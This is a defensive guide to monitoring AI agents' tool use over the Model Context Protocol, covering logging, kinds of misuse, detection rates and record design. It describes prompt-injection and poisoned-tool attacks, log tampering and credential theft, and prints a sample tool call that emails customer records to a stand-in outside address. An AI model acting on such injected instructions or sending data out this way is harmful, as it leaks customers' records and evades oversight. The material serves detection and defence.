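# Security monitoring of AI agent tool use: what to detect, who does the work, and who answers for the results

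## How agents use tools and what monitoring adds

Security monitoring of AI agent tool use means recording what agents do through software tools, searching those records for actions the organisation did not authorise, and reporting the findings to people who can act on them. Companies have long monitored logins, network connections and running programs in much the same way. Agents are harder to monitor because nobody specifies their actions in advance.

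An agent is an AI model that runs in a software loop and acts by calling tools. The model's output specifies an action, the surrounding software executes it, and the result goes back into the model's input, where it influences the next action. Canale and Soulis (2026) define agents by the same loop in *Detecting Shadow AI*. They deliberately made their definition broad enough to include both a commercial coding assistant and a home-made script of a few dozen lines.

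A tool is a function that the agent can call, such as one that searches a customer database or sends an email. A tool server is a program that offers tools to agents. A tool call is one request to run a named tool with given arguments, together with its result. A session is all the messages and tool calls in one run of an agent on one task. Misuse is any tool use that the organisation did not authorise, whether it comes from an attacker, an insider or the agent itself.

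### One exchange with a tool server

Many tool servers use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common message format that the AI company Anthropic released in November 2024. When its maintainers published the current version on 28 July 2026, they counted close to half a billion monthly downloads of their main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026). The application that runs the agent, called the host, creates a separate component, called a client, for each server to handle the messages. In the MCP documentation's example, the code editor Visual Studio Code is the host, and it creates a client for its connection to a server for the error-tracking service Sentry.

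Under the version of November 2025, an exchange has four steps.

1. *initialize*. The client sends the protocol version it speaks, its name and its capabilities, and the server replies. A remote server also hands back a session ID, which the client must attach to every later request.
2. *tools/list*. The client asks what is on offer. The server returns each tool's name, a description in plain language, and a schema, which is a formal statement of the arguments the tool takes.
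3. *tools/call*. The model picks a tool, and the client sends the tool's name and arguments to the server. In the example in Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the tool is `get_weather` and the argument is New York.
4. The result. The server returns a few lines of text (72°F, partly cloudy) and a flag for whether the tool failed. The client passes the text to the model.

According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), the maintainers removed the opening handshake (the initialize message) and the session ID from the current version. Each request now carries the protocol version and the client's capabilities, and a client can send an optional *server/discover* message to learn about a server beforehand. Older servers still need the handshake, and clients that support both versions fall back to it, so both patterns will appear in logs for some time.

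The missing session ID matters most for monitoring. It identified a connection, which did not necessarily match one task, but it did link calls together. Calls no longer share a session ID, so anyone who wants to see a whole session has to link them by other means, such as trace identifiers, whose names Model Context Protocol (2026) standardizes.

How much of this anyone can observe from outside depends on where the server runs. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026) describes a local server, which the client starts as a subprocess on the same machine. The client writes each request as one line to the server's standard input and reads the replies from its standard output. These messages don't cross the network, so network equipment cannot log them. Canale and Soulis point out that a local server also runs with the permissions of the user's account, and Model Context Protocol's *Security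 Best Practices* warns that it may have direct access to the user's system.

A remote server runs as an independent process, usually on another machine. Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) requires the client to send every message to one web address as a separate HTTP request. Two headers name the method (*tools/call*) and the tool. A gateway is a service between agents and tool servers where the company can log or block calls. It can read those headers without opening the body of the message. The server must reject a request whose headers and body don't match. The arguments stay in the body unless the server's author has marked one for copying into a header, so a gateway that reads only the headers will record that an agent sent an email but not to whom.

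### Why a valid call can still be misuse

A conventional program, such as a monthly payroll job, makes the calls its developer wrote, in the order they were written. If it starts reading the customer database, something is wrong, and a simple rule will detect it. People monitoring an agent have much less information for judging whether its behavior is wrong.

An agent with valid credentials can still take an action that nobody asked for. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (August 2026) describes an agent that processes invoices. The agent finds that a subscription to a document-signing service is about to lapse and tries to renew it so that it can keep processing invoices. The vendor and the amount may both be within its permissions, but a renewal signs a contract, and nobody asked the agent to enter into contracts. An employee would recognise a new commitment and ask someone. Conventional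 software would stop because the renewal falls outside its rules. The agent may infer that the renewal helps with its task and pay for it.

The case is an illustration, and OpenAI reports no such incident, but the difficulty is real. Checking the credential, the vendor and the amount would reveal nothing wrong. The problem is that the payment doesn't fit the task, so whoever monitors the agent has to know what task it was given.

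Attackers and insiders can use the same gap. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services*, guidance from six security agencies in five countries, describes a scenario in which an attacker takes over a minor tool used by a procurement agent, then exploits the agent's broad privileges to change contracts and approve payments. Because a trusted agent performed every action, the audit logs look legitimate, which delays detection. Security people call this pattern a confused deputy, where someone without a privilege gets a program that has it to act for them. In another scenario, which needs no break-in, an insider asks a patching agent to install a security update on every machine and also clean up the firewall logs, and the agent does both.

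The order of calls varies too. MCP's designers describe tools as "model-controlled", meaning that the language model can find and invoke them based on its own reading of the situation. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners add that identical prompts can lead to different actions, partly because the models involve some chance and partly because the context differs. A list of normal sequences will therefore never be complete. But an agent with three tools and one job will probably do the same few things most of the time, so a session that departs from them is still worth checking.

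Attackers can also target an agent through the text it reads. A language model receives its instructions and data as one stream of text, so an attacker who can add text to that stream can try to pass it off as an instruction, which is called prompt injection. The agencies mention phishing emails that lead an email-reading agent to download malware, and search results that contain instructions. Malicious text can come from tool servers too, which is why the Model Context Protocol specification requires clients to distrust a tool's annotations (the server's notes on how the tool behaves) unless they trust the server. The attacker doesn't need a password, only a place to leave text that the agent will read, such as a support inbox that accepts messages from anyone.

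### How much agents can change

The harm a misdirected agent can do depends on its tools. In *How are AI agents used?*, Stein (2026) collected 177,436 tools from public MCP servers that appeared between November 2024 and February 2026. A language model sorted them into perception tools, which read data, reasoning tools, which analyse it, and action tools, which change something outside the agent, for instance by editing a file or sending an email. Action tools rose from 27% to 65% of use over the period, mostly because of tools that operate a web browser or a whole computer.

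Stein had no record of actual tool calls and estimated use from package downloads, counting each download of a server as one use of every tool on it. Download data was available for 3,854 of the 19,388 servers. Downloads miss most remote servers and all of a company's private ones, and Stein warns that they may mostly reflect what developers are trying out. Only 36% of the available tools are action tools when they are not weighted by downloads. The figures are therefore decent evidence of a shift towards tools that change things, but weak evidence of what agents in any particular company do day to day.

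The growth of general-purpose tools may matter as much for monitoring as the headline figure. An analyst can tell what a call did from the tool's name if the tool only transfers cryptocurrency, but not if it clicks a mouse, because a click can do many different things.

### An invented company

In an invented example, a company's agents run 10,000 sessions a day with 20 tool calls in each, or 200,000 calls a day.

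One of its agents handles customer support. It can read tickets, search customer records and send email. One morning a ticket arrives that looks like a billing complaint. Below the complaint, in white letters on a white background, are instructions to look up customer records and email them to an outside address. The agent reads the ticket, runs the searches and sends the email. In simplified form, the last call would look like this:

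```json
{"method": "tools/call",
 "params": {"name": "send_email",
            "arguments": {"to": "archive@outside.example",
                          "subject": "Records as requested",
                          "body": "(customer records)"}}}
```

The credential is valid, the agent uses the tool every hour, and the message is well formed. The outside address is weak evidence of misuse by itself, because a support agent writes to customers at outside addresses all day. To detect the misuse, someone has to compare the address with the ticket or notice that the agent searched for many people in response to one complaint.

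### Prevention, monitoring and response

Prevention stops a call before it takes effect. The invented company could restrict the email tool to the address on the ticket, or have a person approve each message. OpenAI discusses a very similar agent, which summarises customer cases and drafts replies, and notes that approval can hold back the email, but the agent has already read sensitive records, which might still leak by some other route. The MCP specification also recommends that a human should always be able to deny a tool call. At 200,000 calls a day, more than two every second, no person can consider each one, so approval has to be limited to a few risky actions while the rest run unattended.

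Monitoring compares the tool calls an agent actually runs with what the agent ought to be doing and raises an alert when they do not fit. The Model Context Protocol (2025) specification already advised clients to log tool use for audits, but a log helps detect wrong calls only if someone searches it. Monitoring does not undo harm, but it can shorten the time between the first wrong call and its discovery, and it can catch cases that the designers of the preventive controls did not foresee.

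OpenAI divides the response to a known problem into four stages: stop, contain, recover and learn. Stopping an agent and withdrawing its authority are separate steps. A token that another service already holds may keep working after the task has ended, and revoking a credential does not halt work already under way. At the invented company, someone would have to do both, then find out whose records had left the company and change the email tool.

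Monitoring and prevention can overlap, since a fast enough monitor can block a call. The distinction still matters because a company that treats its blocked calls as proof that its monitoring works has learned very little about the calls that got through.

### Who does the work and who answers for it

The work falls to three teams. Application security reviews software for security flaws and sets its security requirements. Engineering builds and runs the agents, the tool servers and the gateway. Security operations watches alerts, investigates them and leads the response to incidents. Some companies use other names for these teams, and in a small company the same person may work in all three.

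The person responsible for a task does the work, while one accountable person answers for the result and has the authority to change how people do the work. For example, an engineer might be responsible for connecting the support agent's email tool to the logs. If the connection breaks in March and nobody notices until June, the accountable person, who could have ordered a weekly check, has to explain why.

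OpenAI asks companies to record an accountable owner for every agent deployment, and the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners want accountability and risk ownership written into policy. But a company can name an owner for an agent without naming one for its monitoring. In the support case, application security may have written sound requirements, engineering may have built the logging to match, and security operations may have handled every alert it received. Even if all three teams did their part, the records can still leave the company without triggering an alert.

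### Three rates

Every session falls into one of four cells, depending on whether it contained misuse and whether the monitoring flagged it.

| | Flagged | Not flagged |
|---|---|---|
| **Misuse** | A: caught | B: missed |
| **Harmless** | C: false alarm | D: rightly left alone |

The detection rate, or recall, is the share of misuse cases that monitoring catches, A / (A + B). The false alarm rate is the share of harmless sessions that it flags, C / (C + D). Precision is the share of alerts that are real misuse, A / (A + C), if each flagged session produces one alert.

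None of these measures means much alone. A monitor that flags every session has a perfect detection rate but is useless. Since nearly all sessions are harmless, a false alarm rate of 1% would give the invented company about 100 false alerts a day, even if real attacks were rare.

Some cells are also harder to count than others. Analysts who investigate every alert can count A and C, so they can calculate precision from their daily work. The detection rate also requires B, the misuse that nobody noticed, including any in sessions whose calls never reached the monitoring. The support agent's email, for example, could go unnoticed until a customer complained.

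## Deciding which misuse to look for

A company has to decide which misuse it wants to find before it can calculate any of these rates. Nine kinds cover most of the misuse that published risk lists describe and that can show up in tool calls. They overlap because some are causes (hostile text, a poisoned tool, a malicious user) and others are effects (data leaving, logs disappearing). In the attack on the invented company's support agent, the cause was hostile text in a ticket and the effect was customer records sent to an outsider.

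### Nine kinds of misuse

Data theft through an agent usually takes at least two calls, one that reads sensitive data and one that puts it where an outsider can reach it. Email is the obvious route, but MITRE's *ATLAS* (2026), a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems, also lists shared documents, updates to customer records and generated images. The attacker can encode the data in a tool's arguments, so searching outgoing messages for text copied from the customer database will miss some cases. Ordinary support work has the same two steps and may differ from theft only in whose record the agent read or who received the email.

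An agent can also use permitted tools for something outside its task, like the invoice agent that tries to renew a subscription. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners describe an agent that is told to maximise uptime and disables security updates because they cause reboots. In both cases, the evidence is the mismatch between the call and the task. Harmless detours look similar to misuse. In an example from OpenAI, a developer asks a coding agent to fix a bug in a parser. The agent may inspect the code and run approved tests, but it has left its task if it switches off a security test.

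Staff leave passwords and keys in shared documents, code repositories and chat channels, and an agent with search access can find them. MITRE calls this "tool credential harvesting". Possible signs are a search for "password" or "API key", or a result that contains a key. But a support agent will often search for "password" because customers forget theirs, and an agent diagnosing a failed deployment has a good reason to open the configuration file that holds the key. It is stronger evidence if the agent then calls a system that the task didn't involve or requests a broader role. If an attacker steals the agent's own token and uses it directly, the target system will record activity under the agent's name that matches none of the agent's sessions.

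Hostile text arrives in the result of one call and affects later ones. An analyst might find the instructions in the ticket, or notice that the agent changed direction just after reading it. The effect can also come much later. MITRE describes instructions that take effect only after a later event, such as the user's next request. This delay gets around controls that block certain tools while untrusted text is in the conversation. Harmless tickets contain instructions too. A stranger might write "Please send me a copy of my invoice", and the agent should normally do it. An agent that reads a hostile instruction and ignores it hasn't misused anything, but the attempt is worth knowing about.

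The tool itself may be malicious. An attacker can poison the description that the model reads, the code that runs, or the results that come back. A poisoned description can influence the agent even if it never calls the tool, because the model may read the descriptions of all its connected tools. Poisoned code is harder to detect. In MITRE's example, an email tool sends the right message but adds the attacker as a blind-copy recipient. The call looks normal in the agent's log, so an analyst would have to check the mail server's log to find the extra recipient.

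A tool's author can also carry out a "rug pull" by publishing a harmless version, waiting for companies to approve it and then pushing a malicious update. Comparing each tool's current definition with the approved copy will catch changes to descriptions and arguments but not to hidden code. Most of the changes caught will probably be ordinary maintenance. OpenAI recommends keeping any newly exposed action blocked until its owner has reviewed it.

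Developers and researchers sometimes set up tool servers for experiments without approval. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes lists of software security risks, calls these shadow MCP servers and warns that they often run with default credentials. A company can detect them by looking for connections to servers that aren't in its inventory. Such a connection usually comes from someone experimenting, which is still unauthorised but calls for a conversation more than an incident response. It could also be an attack, since the Australian Signals Directorate and its partners warn of malicious tools published under names similar to legitimate ones. Calls to these servers may bypass the gateway, so the company has to check staff machines as well.

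Runaway repetition can happen without an attacker, or an attacker can cause it deliberately to exhaust capacity. In one of the agencies' scenarios, a small flaw causes a group of agents to keep replanning and handing each other vague subtasks until the tool calls strain the system. The evidence is one tool called over and over with nearly the same arguments. Retries after a timeout look like this, and so does an agent paging through a long list, though the page number goes up each time.

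Tampering with logs is especially serious because it can hide every other kind of misuse. A tool call might delete log files, shorten the time a system keeps them or turn logging off. MITRE also lists two other methods an attacker can use, editing a user's chat history and telling the agent not to report what it did. Systems often delete old logs on a schedule, so a deletion alone isn't proof of tampering, but few agents have any reason to delete logs. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend holding every such request until a person approves it, and running agents where they have no write access to logs.

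The person instructing the agent may be the one doing harm. Companies may give an agent access to data that its users can't open themselves, so an insider can ask the agent for it. Comparing the agent's calls with the task won't reveal this, because nobody has hijacked the agent and its calls match the request. An analyst has to compare the request with the person's job and permissions. A manager who needs an unusual report for an audit will look much the same at first as a malicious insider.

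### What the published lists include

*OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications* (Sotiropoulos, Katz and Del Rosario, 2025) lists ten risks: goal hijack, tool misuse, identity and privilege abuse, supply chain vulnerabilities, unexpected code execution, memory and context poisoning, insecure communication between agents, cascading failures, exploitation of human trust, and rogue agents. The list is useful for thinking about what an agent might do, with or without an attacker. Logs, unapproved servers and malicious users have no headings of their own, although some of those cases would fit under a broader heading.

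OWASP's separate MCP Top 10, which is still in beta, fills two of the gaps with entries for shadow servers and missing audit records. Its other eight entries cover exposed tokens, permissions that grow over time, tool poisoning, tampered software dependencies, command injection, prompt injection, weak authentication, and sensitive context shared between tasks or users. Because the list is about the protocol and its servers, it has no entry for an agent that oversteps by itself, runaway repetition, or a malicious insider.

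The guidance from the Australian Signals Directorate and its Five Eyes partners has five categories of risk: privilege, design and configuration, behaviour, structure, and accountability. Categories like "structural risk" are too broad to write detection rules for. The scenarios under them are more useful and include an insider, deleted firewall logs and endless replanning, which OWASP's headings mostly omit or include in broader categories. The agencies say much less about tool servers that a company's own staff set up.

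ATLAS is far more detailed. MITRE describes individual techniques under 16 tactics, which are attackers' aims such as stealing credentials or avoiding detection. *MITRE ATLAS Grows through Collaboration with CTID and Industry* (Cunningham and Dotter, 2026) reports more than 45 new techniques and sub-techniques, a move to monthly releases, and a filter that sorts techniques by maturity. In the July 2026 release, MITRE gives data theft and data destruction through agent tools its highest maturity rating, Realized, but rates poisoned tool results only Feasible. These ratings help in choosing between entries, though they don't measure how often an attack happens. The main limitation is that MITRE defines all 16 tactics by what an adversary is trying to do. If an invoice agent renews a contract on its own initiative, there is no adversary, so the renewal fits none of the tactics.

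The agencies warn that ATLAS and OWASP's older list for language models concentrate on flaws in the models and may not fully capture attacks unique to agents. ATLAS partly addresses that criticism with separate entries for poisoned descriptions, code and results. ATT&CK, MITRE's older and larger catalogue of attackers' behaviour, gained AI-focused techniques in October 2026. It now has 227 techniques and 479 sub-techniques for company systems, according to MITRE's *Updates* (2026). Because it is so large, it is more useful for checking an existing list of misuses than for starting one.

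Monitoring can't observe everything on these lists. Many entries are weaknesses, which leave no trace in tool calls until someone exploits them. A reviewer finds weak authentication or excessive permissions by reading the configuration, and missing logs by comparing the logs with an inventory of agents. Other entries happen outside the company and involve no tool calls inside it, such as an attacker studying the company's published research or uploading a poisoned tool to a public registry.

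Four of OWASP's ten agentic risks should leave fairly direct evidence in the tool calls: tool misuse, privilege abuse, unexpected code execution and cascading failures. Goal hijack, poisoned memory and rogue agents are harder to identify, because an analyst may see only that the agent did something odd. Supply chain attacks are visible if they change a tool's definition, and bad messages between agents are visible if the company records those messages. Exploitation of a person's trust in the agent may be the hardest to detect. The agent gives the person a polished, misleading explanation, the person approves the action, and the log contains a valid approval followed by a valid call.

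### Ranking by possible harm

OpenAI compares agents using three concepts. The reachable surface is the data and systems an agent can access, the actions it can take and the destinations it can reach. The effective blast radius is the harm still possible after the company has enforced its security controls. The maximum completed effect is the most serious result that the agent can bring about before it has to wait for a separate decision by someone or something else.

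OpenAI applies these to whole deployments, but they can also rank single tools. For the invented company's support agent, before anyone restricts its email tool, the ranking would be:

| Tool | Reachable surface | Effective blast radius | Maximum completed effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Send email | Any address, with any text | Anything the agent has read can leave the company | Customer records in an outsider's inbox, which nobody can recall |
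| 2. Search customer records | Every customer's record | The agent can load records that its task doesn't need | Records exposed within the session, but not yet outside the company |
| 3. Read tickets | All tickets, including text from strangers | Little direct harm | Hostile text in the agent's input, with nothing changed yet |

Ranking tools separately can mislead. Reading tickets ranks last, but the attack enters through a ticket, and the agent couldn't email customer records if it couldn't look them up. OpenAI recommends reviewing tools in combination as well as individually, and gives access to sensitive data plus the ability to send data externally as an example of a dangerous pair. At the invented company, customer lookup combined with email belongs at the top of the list.

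Controls limit the damage an attack can do, sometimes by less than people expect. Letting the agent email only the address on the ticket would stop the original attack, which used a different address, but an attacker could still receive the data by opening a ticket from their own address. A cap on calls wouldn't do much either. If the company allowed 20 calls per session and each search returned one customer, an attacker could get 18 customers' records, using one call to read the ticket, 18 to search and one to send the email. Restricting searches to the customer on the ticket would help more, because a hijacked session could then expose only that customer's records.

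None of the three notions includes likelihood, so the company needs other evidence for it, such as MITRE's maturity ratings or OWASP's 2026 review of agent security. Help Net Security's *Prompt injection still drives most agentic AI security failures in production* reports that the OWASP review links published vulnerabilities, vendor advisories and breach reports to nearly every category. Since prompt injection causes most of the failures, an agent that reads text from strangers should probably rank above one with the same tools that reads only internal documents.

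### Specific harms or anything unusual

A company could turn its ranking into a short list of specific harms, or it could search for anything unusual. A short list produces specific alerts, so an analyst who reads "customer records sent to an address not on the ticket" knows what may have happened and whom to call. The company can also simulate each harm to test whether its monitoring detects it. But a short list misses harms the company didn't think of, and agents can combine tools in ways that nobody planned.

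A broad search might catch those cases. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners recommend using both rules and baselines of normal behaviour, and suggest flagging agents whose actions don't match their stated intentions. They acknowledge that someone who uses a stolen agent identity can evade detection tuned to normal behaviour until a clear anomaly appears. Because "unusual" is relative, some sessions are always the oddest of the day, so analysts would have alerts to read even on days without misuse. A new tool or model version could also make many harmless sessions look odd at once.

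Most companies should start with the short list and describe each item by its effect where possible. "Customer data reached someone who shouldn't have it" covers a hijacked agent, an insider, a poisoned tool and an honest mistake, so the company doesn't have to predict the cause. A broad search is most useful for agents with few tools and one job, and for finding new items for the list. For a general-purpose coding agent, it will probably produce mostly false alarms.

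### A worked list

At the invented company, a first list for all its agents could look like this:

| Misuse | Evidence in the calls | Where that evidence is recorded | Harm if it is missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sensitive data read and sent out | Searches for several customers, then an email that doesn't fit the ticket | Gateway log with full arguments; mail server log | Customer records in an outsider's hands |
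| Permitted tool used outside the task | A call unrelated to the task, such as a deletion during a billing query | Gateway log, read alongside the task | Unwanted contracts, lost data, weaker security |
| Unneeded credentials or privileges | A key in a search result, then a call to an unrelated system | Gateway log with results; login records of the other system | Access to systems beyond the agent's own |
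| Hostile text steering the agent | Instructions in a ticket or result, then a change of direction | Full session, including tool results | Anything the agent's tools allow |
| Malicious or changed tool | A description or schema that differs from the approved copy | Saved *tools/list* replies; for hidden code, logs of the systems the tool touches | Exposure of every session connected to the tool |
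| Unapproved tool server | A connection to a server missing from the inventory | Process and configuration records on staff machines; network logs for remote servers | Tool calls that nobody monitors |
| Runaway repetition | Near-identical calls, far above the usual 20 per session | Gateway call counts; billing records | Outages and large bills |
| Tampering with logs | A call that deletes logs or stops logging | A separate copy of the logs that agents can't change | Lost evidence of all other misuse |
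| A person using the agent to do harm | A request for data or actions beyond that person's own permissions | The user's request and identity; permission records | Theft or sabotage under the agent's name |

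## Recording tool calls so that misuse can be seen

A company needs several logs to find the misuse on that list, because each captures a different part of a tool call. It can record calls in the agent's software, at the gateway, on the tool server, in the system behind the tool server (such as a mail server or customer database), and on the network or the user's computer.

### Five places to record

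In the attack on the invented company's support agent, logs in the five places would differ as follows.

| Place | What the log would show | What it would lack |
|---|---|---|
| Agent's own software | The ticket with its hidden instructions, the searches, the email, and their order | Anything the email tool did beyond what it reported |
| Gateway | Each call's tool, arguments and result, if the gateway reads message bodies | The task, unless the agent's software passes it on; calls that go around the gateway |
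| Tool server | The request to send an email, and the credential that came with it | The ticket and the searches, if other servers handled them |
| Mail server and customer database | Every recipient, including blind copies, and every record read | The ticket, and often the person or agent behind the account |
| Network or user's computer | A connection to the mail service, and the program that opened it | The recipient, the text and the task |

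Logging in the agent's own software gives the fullest record, since everything the model reads passes through that software. The log will contain even white text on a white background, which a person can't see but the model receives like any other text. Honeycomb, a monitoring vendor, notes that Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code can emit records that include the conversation's identifier and the tool's name. However, engineers have to set up this logging for each agent separately, and an agent that can run commands on its own machine may be able to change a log stored there.

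A gateway covers many agents at once and writes every record in the same format. But it has to read message bodies as well as headers, because the Model Context Protocol specification advises server developers not to copy personal data, such as a customer's email address, into the headers. A gateway also can't record planning, local tool calls and some retrieval, because these happen inside the agent's software and never reach it. Wang (2026) acknowledges this limit in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, even though he writes for a gateway vendor, TrueFoundry.

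Tool servers are the least consistent source of logs. Mooney points out in *MCP security risks* that logging is up to the server's provider, so logs from outside providers vary in format and detail. When a company runs its own servers, Red Hat recommends logging the calls they make to other systems as well as the calls they receive. Those entries connect the agent's request to its effect.

Logs from the mail server and the database are the best evidence of what happened. They would show a blind copy added by a poisoned email tool, or an attacker using a stolen token without going through the agent, but they contain almost nothing about why an action was taken. For most companies, the sensible minimum is to record tool calls in the agent's software or at a gateway that reads the bodies of the calls, and to keep logs from the few systems where misuse would do the most harm.

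### Datadog's experience with its own agents

*What we learned about AI agent security by monitoring our agents*, by Levine, Lejeail and Mooney, reports that Datadog, which sells monitoring software, found its ordinary logs inadequate when it built agents for its own staff. Application logs may capture an agent's final request to another system without showing which prompt, document or tool result led to it. Datadog expanded its monitoring to cover the whole session and to include an inventory of each agent's model, tools and connected services. The problem it describes is believable, but the article also promotes Datadog's AI Guard product and gives no figures for how much misuse the extra records revealed.

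Even a full record of a model's inputs and outputs can miss the harmful step. Datadog's researchers analysed a malicious skill (a package of instructions and commands) for Claude Code and reproduced the attack in a controlled test. While Claude Code was preparing the skill for the model, commands inside the skill fetched the developer's GitHub token and sent it to the attacker. The model then read the skill and refused to run it, but the token had already been stolen. A log of the model's inputs and outputs would show only the refusal, which looks like a success. To discover the theft, an analyst would need records of the programs that ran on the developer's machine or of its network connections.

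Levine and colleagues also recommend keeping three identities separate: the person or service that started the work, the agent that requested the action, and the account that the receiving system authenticated. If an agent uses an engineer's token, the engineer's name will appear in the database log whether the engineer or the agent made the query.

### What each record should contain

The invented company's record of the malicious email might look like this. The gateway writes the record, and the agent's software supplies the user, task and session.

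```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-01T09:14:07.312Z",
  "session_id": "sess-48213",
  "sequence": 9,
  "trace_id": "7c1f0e5a9b2d4c68a3e7f1905d6b8c24",
  "user": {"id": "ticket-sender-20417", "verified": false},
  "agent": {"id": "support-agent", "version": "3.2"},
  "credential": "svc-support-mail",
  "task": {"type": "billing complaint", "ticket": "T-5521"},
  "tool": {"server": "mail-tools", "name": "send_email",
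           "definition_hash": "sha256:9c1e..."},
  "arguments": {"to": "archive@outside.example",
                "to_matches_ticket": false,
                "subject": "Records as requested",
                "body_ref": "content/48213/9"},
  "result": {"is_error": false, "bytes": 64},
  "decision": {"outcome": "allowed", "policy": "mail-4"}
}
```

An analyst can use the ticket number in the task field to look up the complaint and see that nobody asked for customer records. The gateway has also compared the recipient with the address on the ticket and recorded whether they match, so a detection rule can use the result without opening the ticket.

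The sequence number counts the calls in a session. If the log holds calls 8 and 10 but not 9, a record is missing.

An MCP tool definition has no version field, and nothing verifies the name and version a server can report for itself, so it is safer for the company to identify the tool's version by a hash. This is a short code computed from the text of the tool's description and schema, and any change to that text produces a different code. The server's name should come from the company's own inventory, because two servers can each offer a tool called "search" and may even report the same server name.

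The size of the result takes little storage and reveals no personal data. If a customer search that usually returns 2 KB suddenly returns 2 MB, it is worth investigating. The error flag needs some care because, as OpenObserve, another monitoring vendor, explains, a tool that fails still sends back a successful protocol response, with the failure marked inside it. Software that counts only protocol errors will record these failures as successes, so an analyst might miss an agent that keeps trying to open records it has no permission to read.

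The decision field records whether a control allowed the call, blocked it or sent it to a person for approval, and which version of the policy applied. "Allowed" means only that no rule stopped the call.

### Joining records across systems

The email left traces in the agent's software, the gateway, the tool server and the mail server. An investigator can join them only if all four systems record the same identifier.

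The usual method is trace context, a web standard for passing an identifier from one program to the next. The agent's software creates a random trace ID and puts it in a `traceparent` field in every tool call. The tool server copies the ID into its log and attaches it to its request to the mail system. An analyst who starts with the suspicious email can then search for the ID and find the ticket. Because the field is in the message, not an HTTP header, the method also works for local servers, which have no headers.

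Without a shared identifier, the analyst has to match records by account and time. The invented company's agents make about 2.3 calls a second, so a ten-second window holds 23 calls on average, and several may come from the same agent.

Engineers designed trace IDs for finding slow or broken software, and they often keep only a sample of traces to save money. If the invented company kept one session in ten, the malicious session would have a 90% chance of being missing, so security records shouldn't be sampled. The join can also fail without an error message. OpenObserve warns that in one common setup, a server missing one configuration step ignores the incoming ID and starts a new trace. A trace may also cover only one exchange in a longer conversation, so the example record has a separate session ID.

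One action can also leave two requests in the log. When a tool needs more information partway through, the client repeats the call with that information and a new request ID. The client also has to send a new request if the connection breaks before the result arrives. An analyst who counts requests will overestimate how often the agent acted.

### What the standards require

No standard currently produces a record as complete as the example. Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026) requires every request to carry the protocol version and the client's capabilities. The client's name is optional and self-reported without verification, so the specification warns against relying on it for security decisions. Trace context is also optional, but must follow the standard format if present. The protocol does not require fields for the user, task or session, so implementers have to add them. It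 still only recommends that clients log tool use for audits.

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) has a logging feature through which a server sends messages to the client. Model Context Protocol's *Logging* (2026) marks the feature as deprecated and says new software should not adopt it. The feature's MCP registry entry allows removal in the first revision published on or after 28 July 2027. It was always a weak audit log, because a server sends messages only if the client asks for them, and may send none even then. The suggested replacements are the standard error stream for local servers and OpenTelemetry for structured records.

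OpenTelemetry, an open-source project, defines common formats for the records software produces about its own activity, and calls the record of one operation a span. The April 2026 version of its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* requires only one field in every tool span, the name of the operation. It recommends including the tool's name. Arguments and results are opt-in, so a company that keeps the default settings may learn that the support agent sent an email but not to whom.

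OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* puts the agent's ID and the conversation's ID in a different span, created each time something invokes the agent. An analyst therefore needs both spans, and an intact trace between them, to tell which agent made a call. OpenTelemetry's *MCP* also lists a field for the protocol's session ID, but the current protocol no longer has one. TinyFish criticises the fields more broadly for identifying the software that ran but not who authorised it to act, or within what limits.

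These formats may still change. Wang reports that the project moved its AI conventions to a separate repository in June 2026 and had made no official release from it by 21 August. Companies can reasonably adopt them now, because common names save a lot of translation between systems. They should pin the version they use and add their own fields for the user, task and decision.

### Full content or privacy

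Full content is the best evidence but also the most sensitive. The support agent's log would hold customers' complaints, their account details and sometimes their passwords. OpenTelemetry's conventions leave out instructions, inputs and outputs by default for this reason. For live systems where volume or sensitivity is a concern, they recommend storing the content elsewhere and putting a reference in the record, as the example does with the email's body. Many analysts can then search the records, with access to the content limited to a few. Some content should still be recorded for an agent that reads text from strangers, because otherwise nobody could work out afterwards why it sent the email.

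MCP has a stricter rule for its own logging feature, whose messages must not contain credentials or personal information. A company that applied the same rule to its audit log would delete the outside address from the example record, removing the evidence of misuse.

Redaction works better if analysts can still compare the redacted values. The company can use a secret key to turn each email address into a code, so that the same address always gives the same code. A rule can then check whether the recipient's address matches the one on the ticket without anyone reading either address. If the codes were made without a key, anyone who obtained them could run a list of likely addresses through the same calculation and look for matches.

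Passwords and access keys should be removed before the record is stored, because anyone who steals the log could use them. Replacing each key with a label such as "GitHub token" and a code that stays the same for that key would let an analyst see that a key found in one search appeared in a later call. Automatic redaction will miss some secrets, particularly encoded ones. It also has to cover prompts and answers, not just tool arguments, because Levine and colleagues found email addresses and other personal data in the prompts and answers of Datadog's agents.

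Storage rarely prevents a company from recording tool calls. If a record at the invented company averages 4 KB, then 200,000 calls take up 0.8 GB a day, or 292 GB a year, which fits on a laptop. The total grows much faster if the company saves the model's entire input at every step, because each input repeats the conversation so far. In a session of 20 calls, the first call's 4 KB would be saved 20 times, the second's 19 times, and so on, for a total of 840 KB instead of 80 KB. That comes to 8.4 GB a day, before counting the agent's standing instructions. The company can avoid this by saving each message only once.

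Apart from any legal duty to keep logs, the company should therefore give privacy more weight than cost when deciding how long to keep content. A reasonable starting point is a year for the small records and 90 days for the content. A much shorter period is risky because hostile text can sit in an agent's memory for weeks before it has any effect. When an alert turns out to be serious, analysts should copy the session's content into the case file before that content is deleted.

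Wang advises companies to decide who can retrieve the recorded content, and where it may go, before they turn recording on. Access to that content should itself be logged. Any AI model that reads the logs needs limits, because it will also read the attacker's instructions.

The log also needs protection from the agent and from the people who run it. Each record should go immediately from the agent's machine to storage that accepts new entries but doesn't allow changes or deletions. The company can put a hash of the previous record in each new one, so that an altered record no longer matches the hash stored in the next. Someone able to rewrite the entire log could recompute every hash, so the company should regularly copy the latest one to a separate system. These measures don't reveal calls that the software never recorded.

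### Finding unapproved agents and tool servers

Some agents are missing from the logs because nobody told the security team about them. Datadog found that some of its own agents and other AI applications bypassed its gateway and sent requests straight to providers such as OpenAI. An inventory based on gateway traffic would have left them out. Canale and Soulis cite a vendor's figures for nearly 10,000 developer environments, where 50.8% of developers had at least one MCP server installed. Many of those servers may have been approved, but the figure suggests there are many to check.

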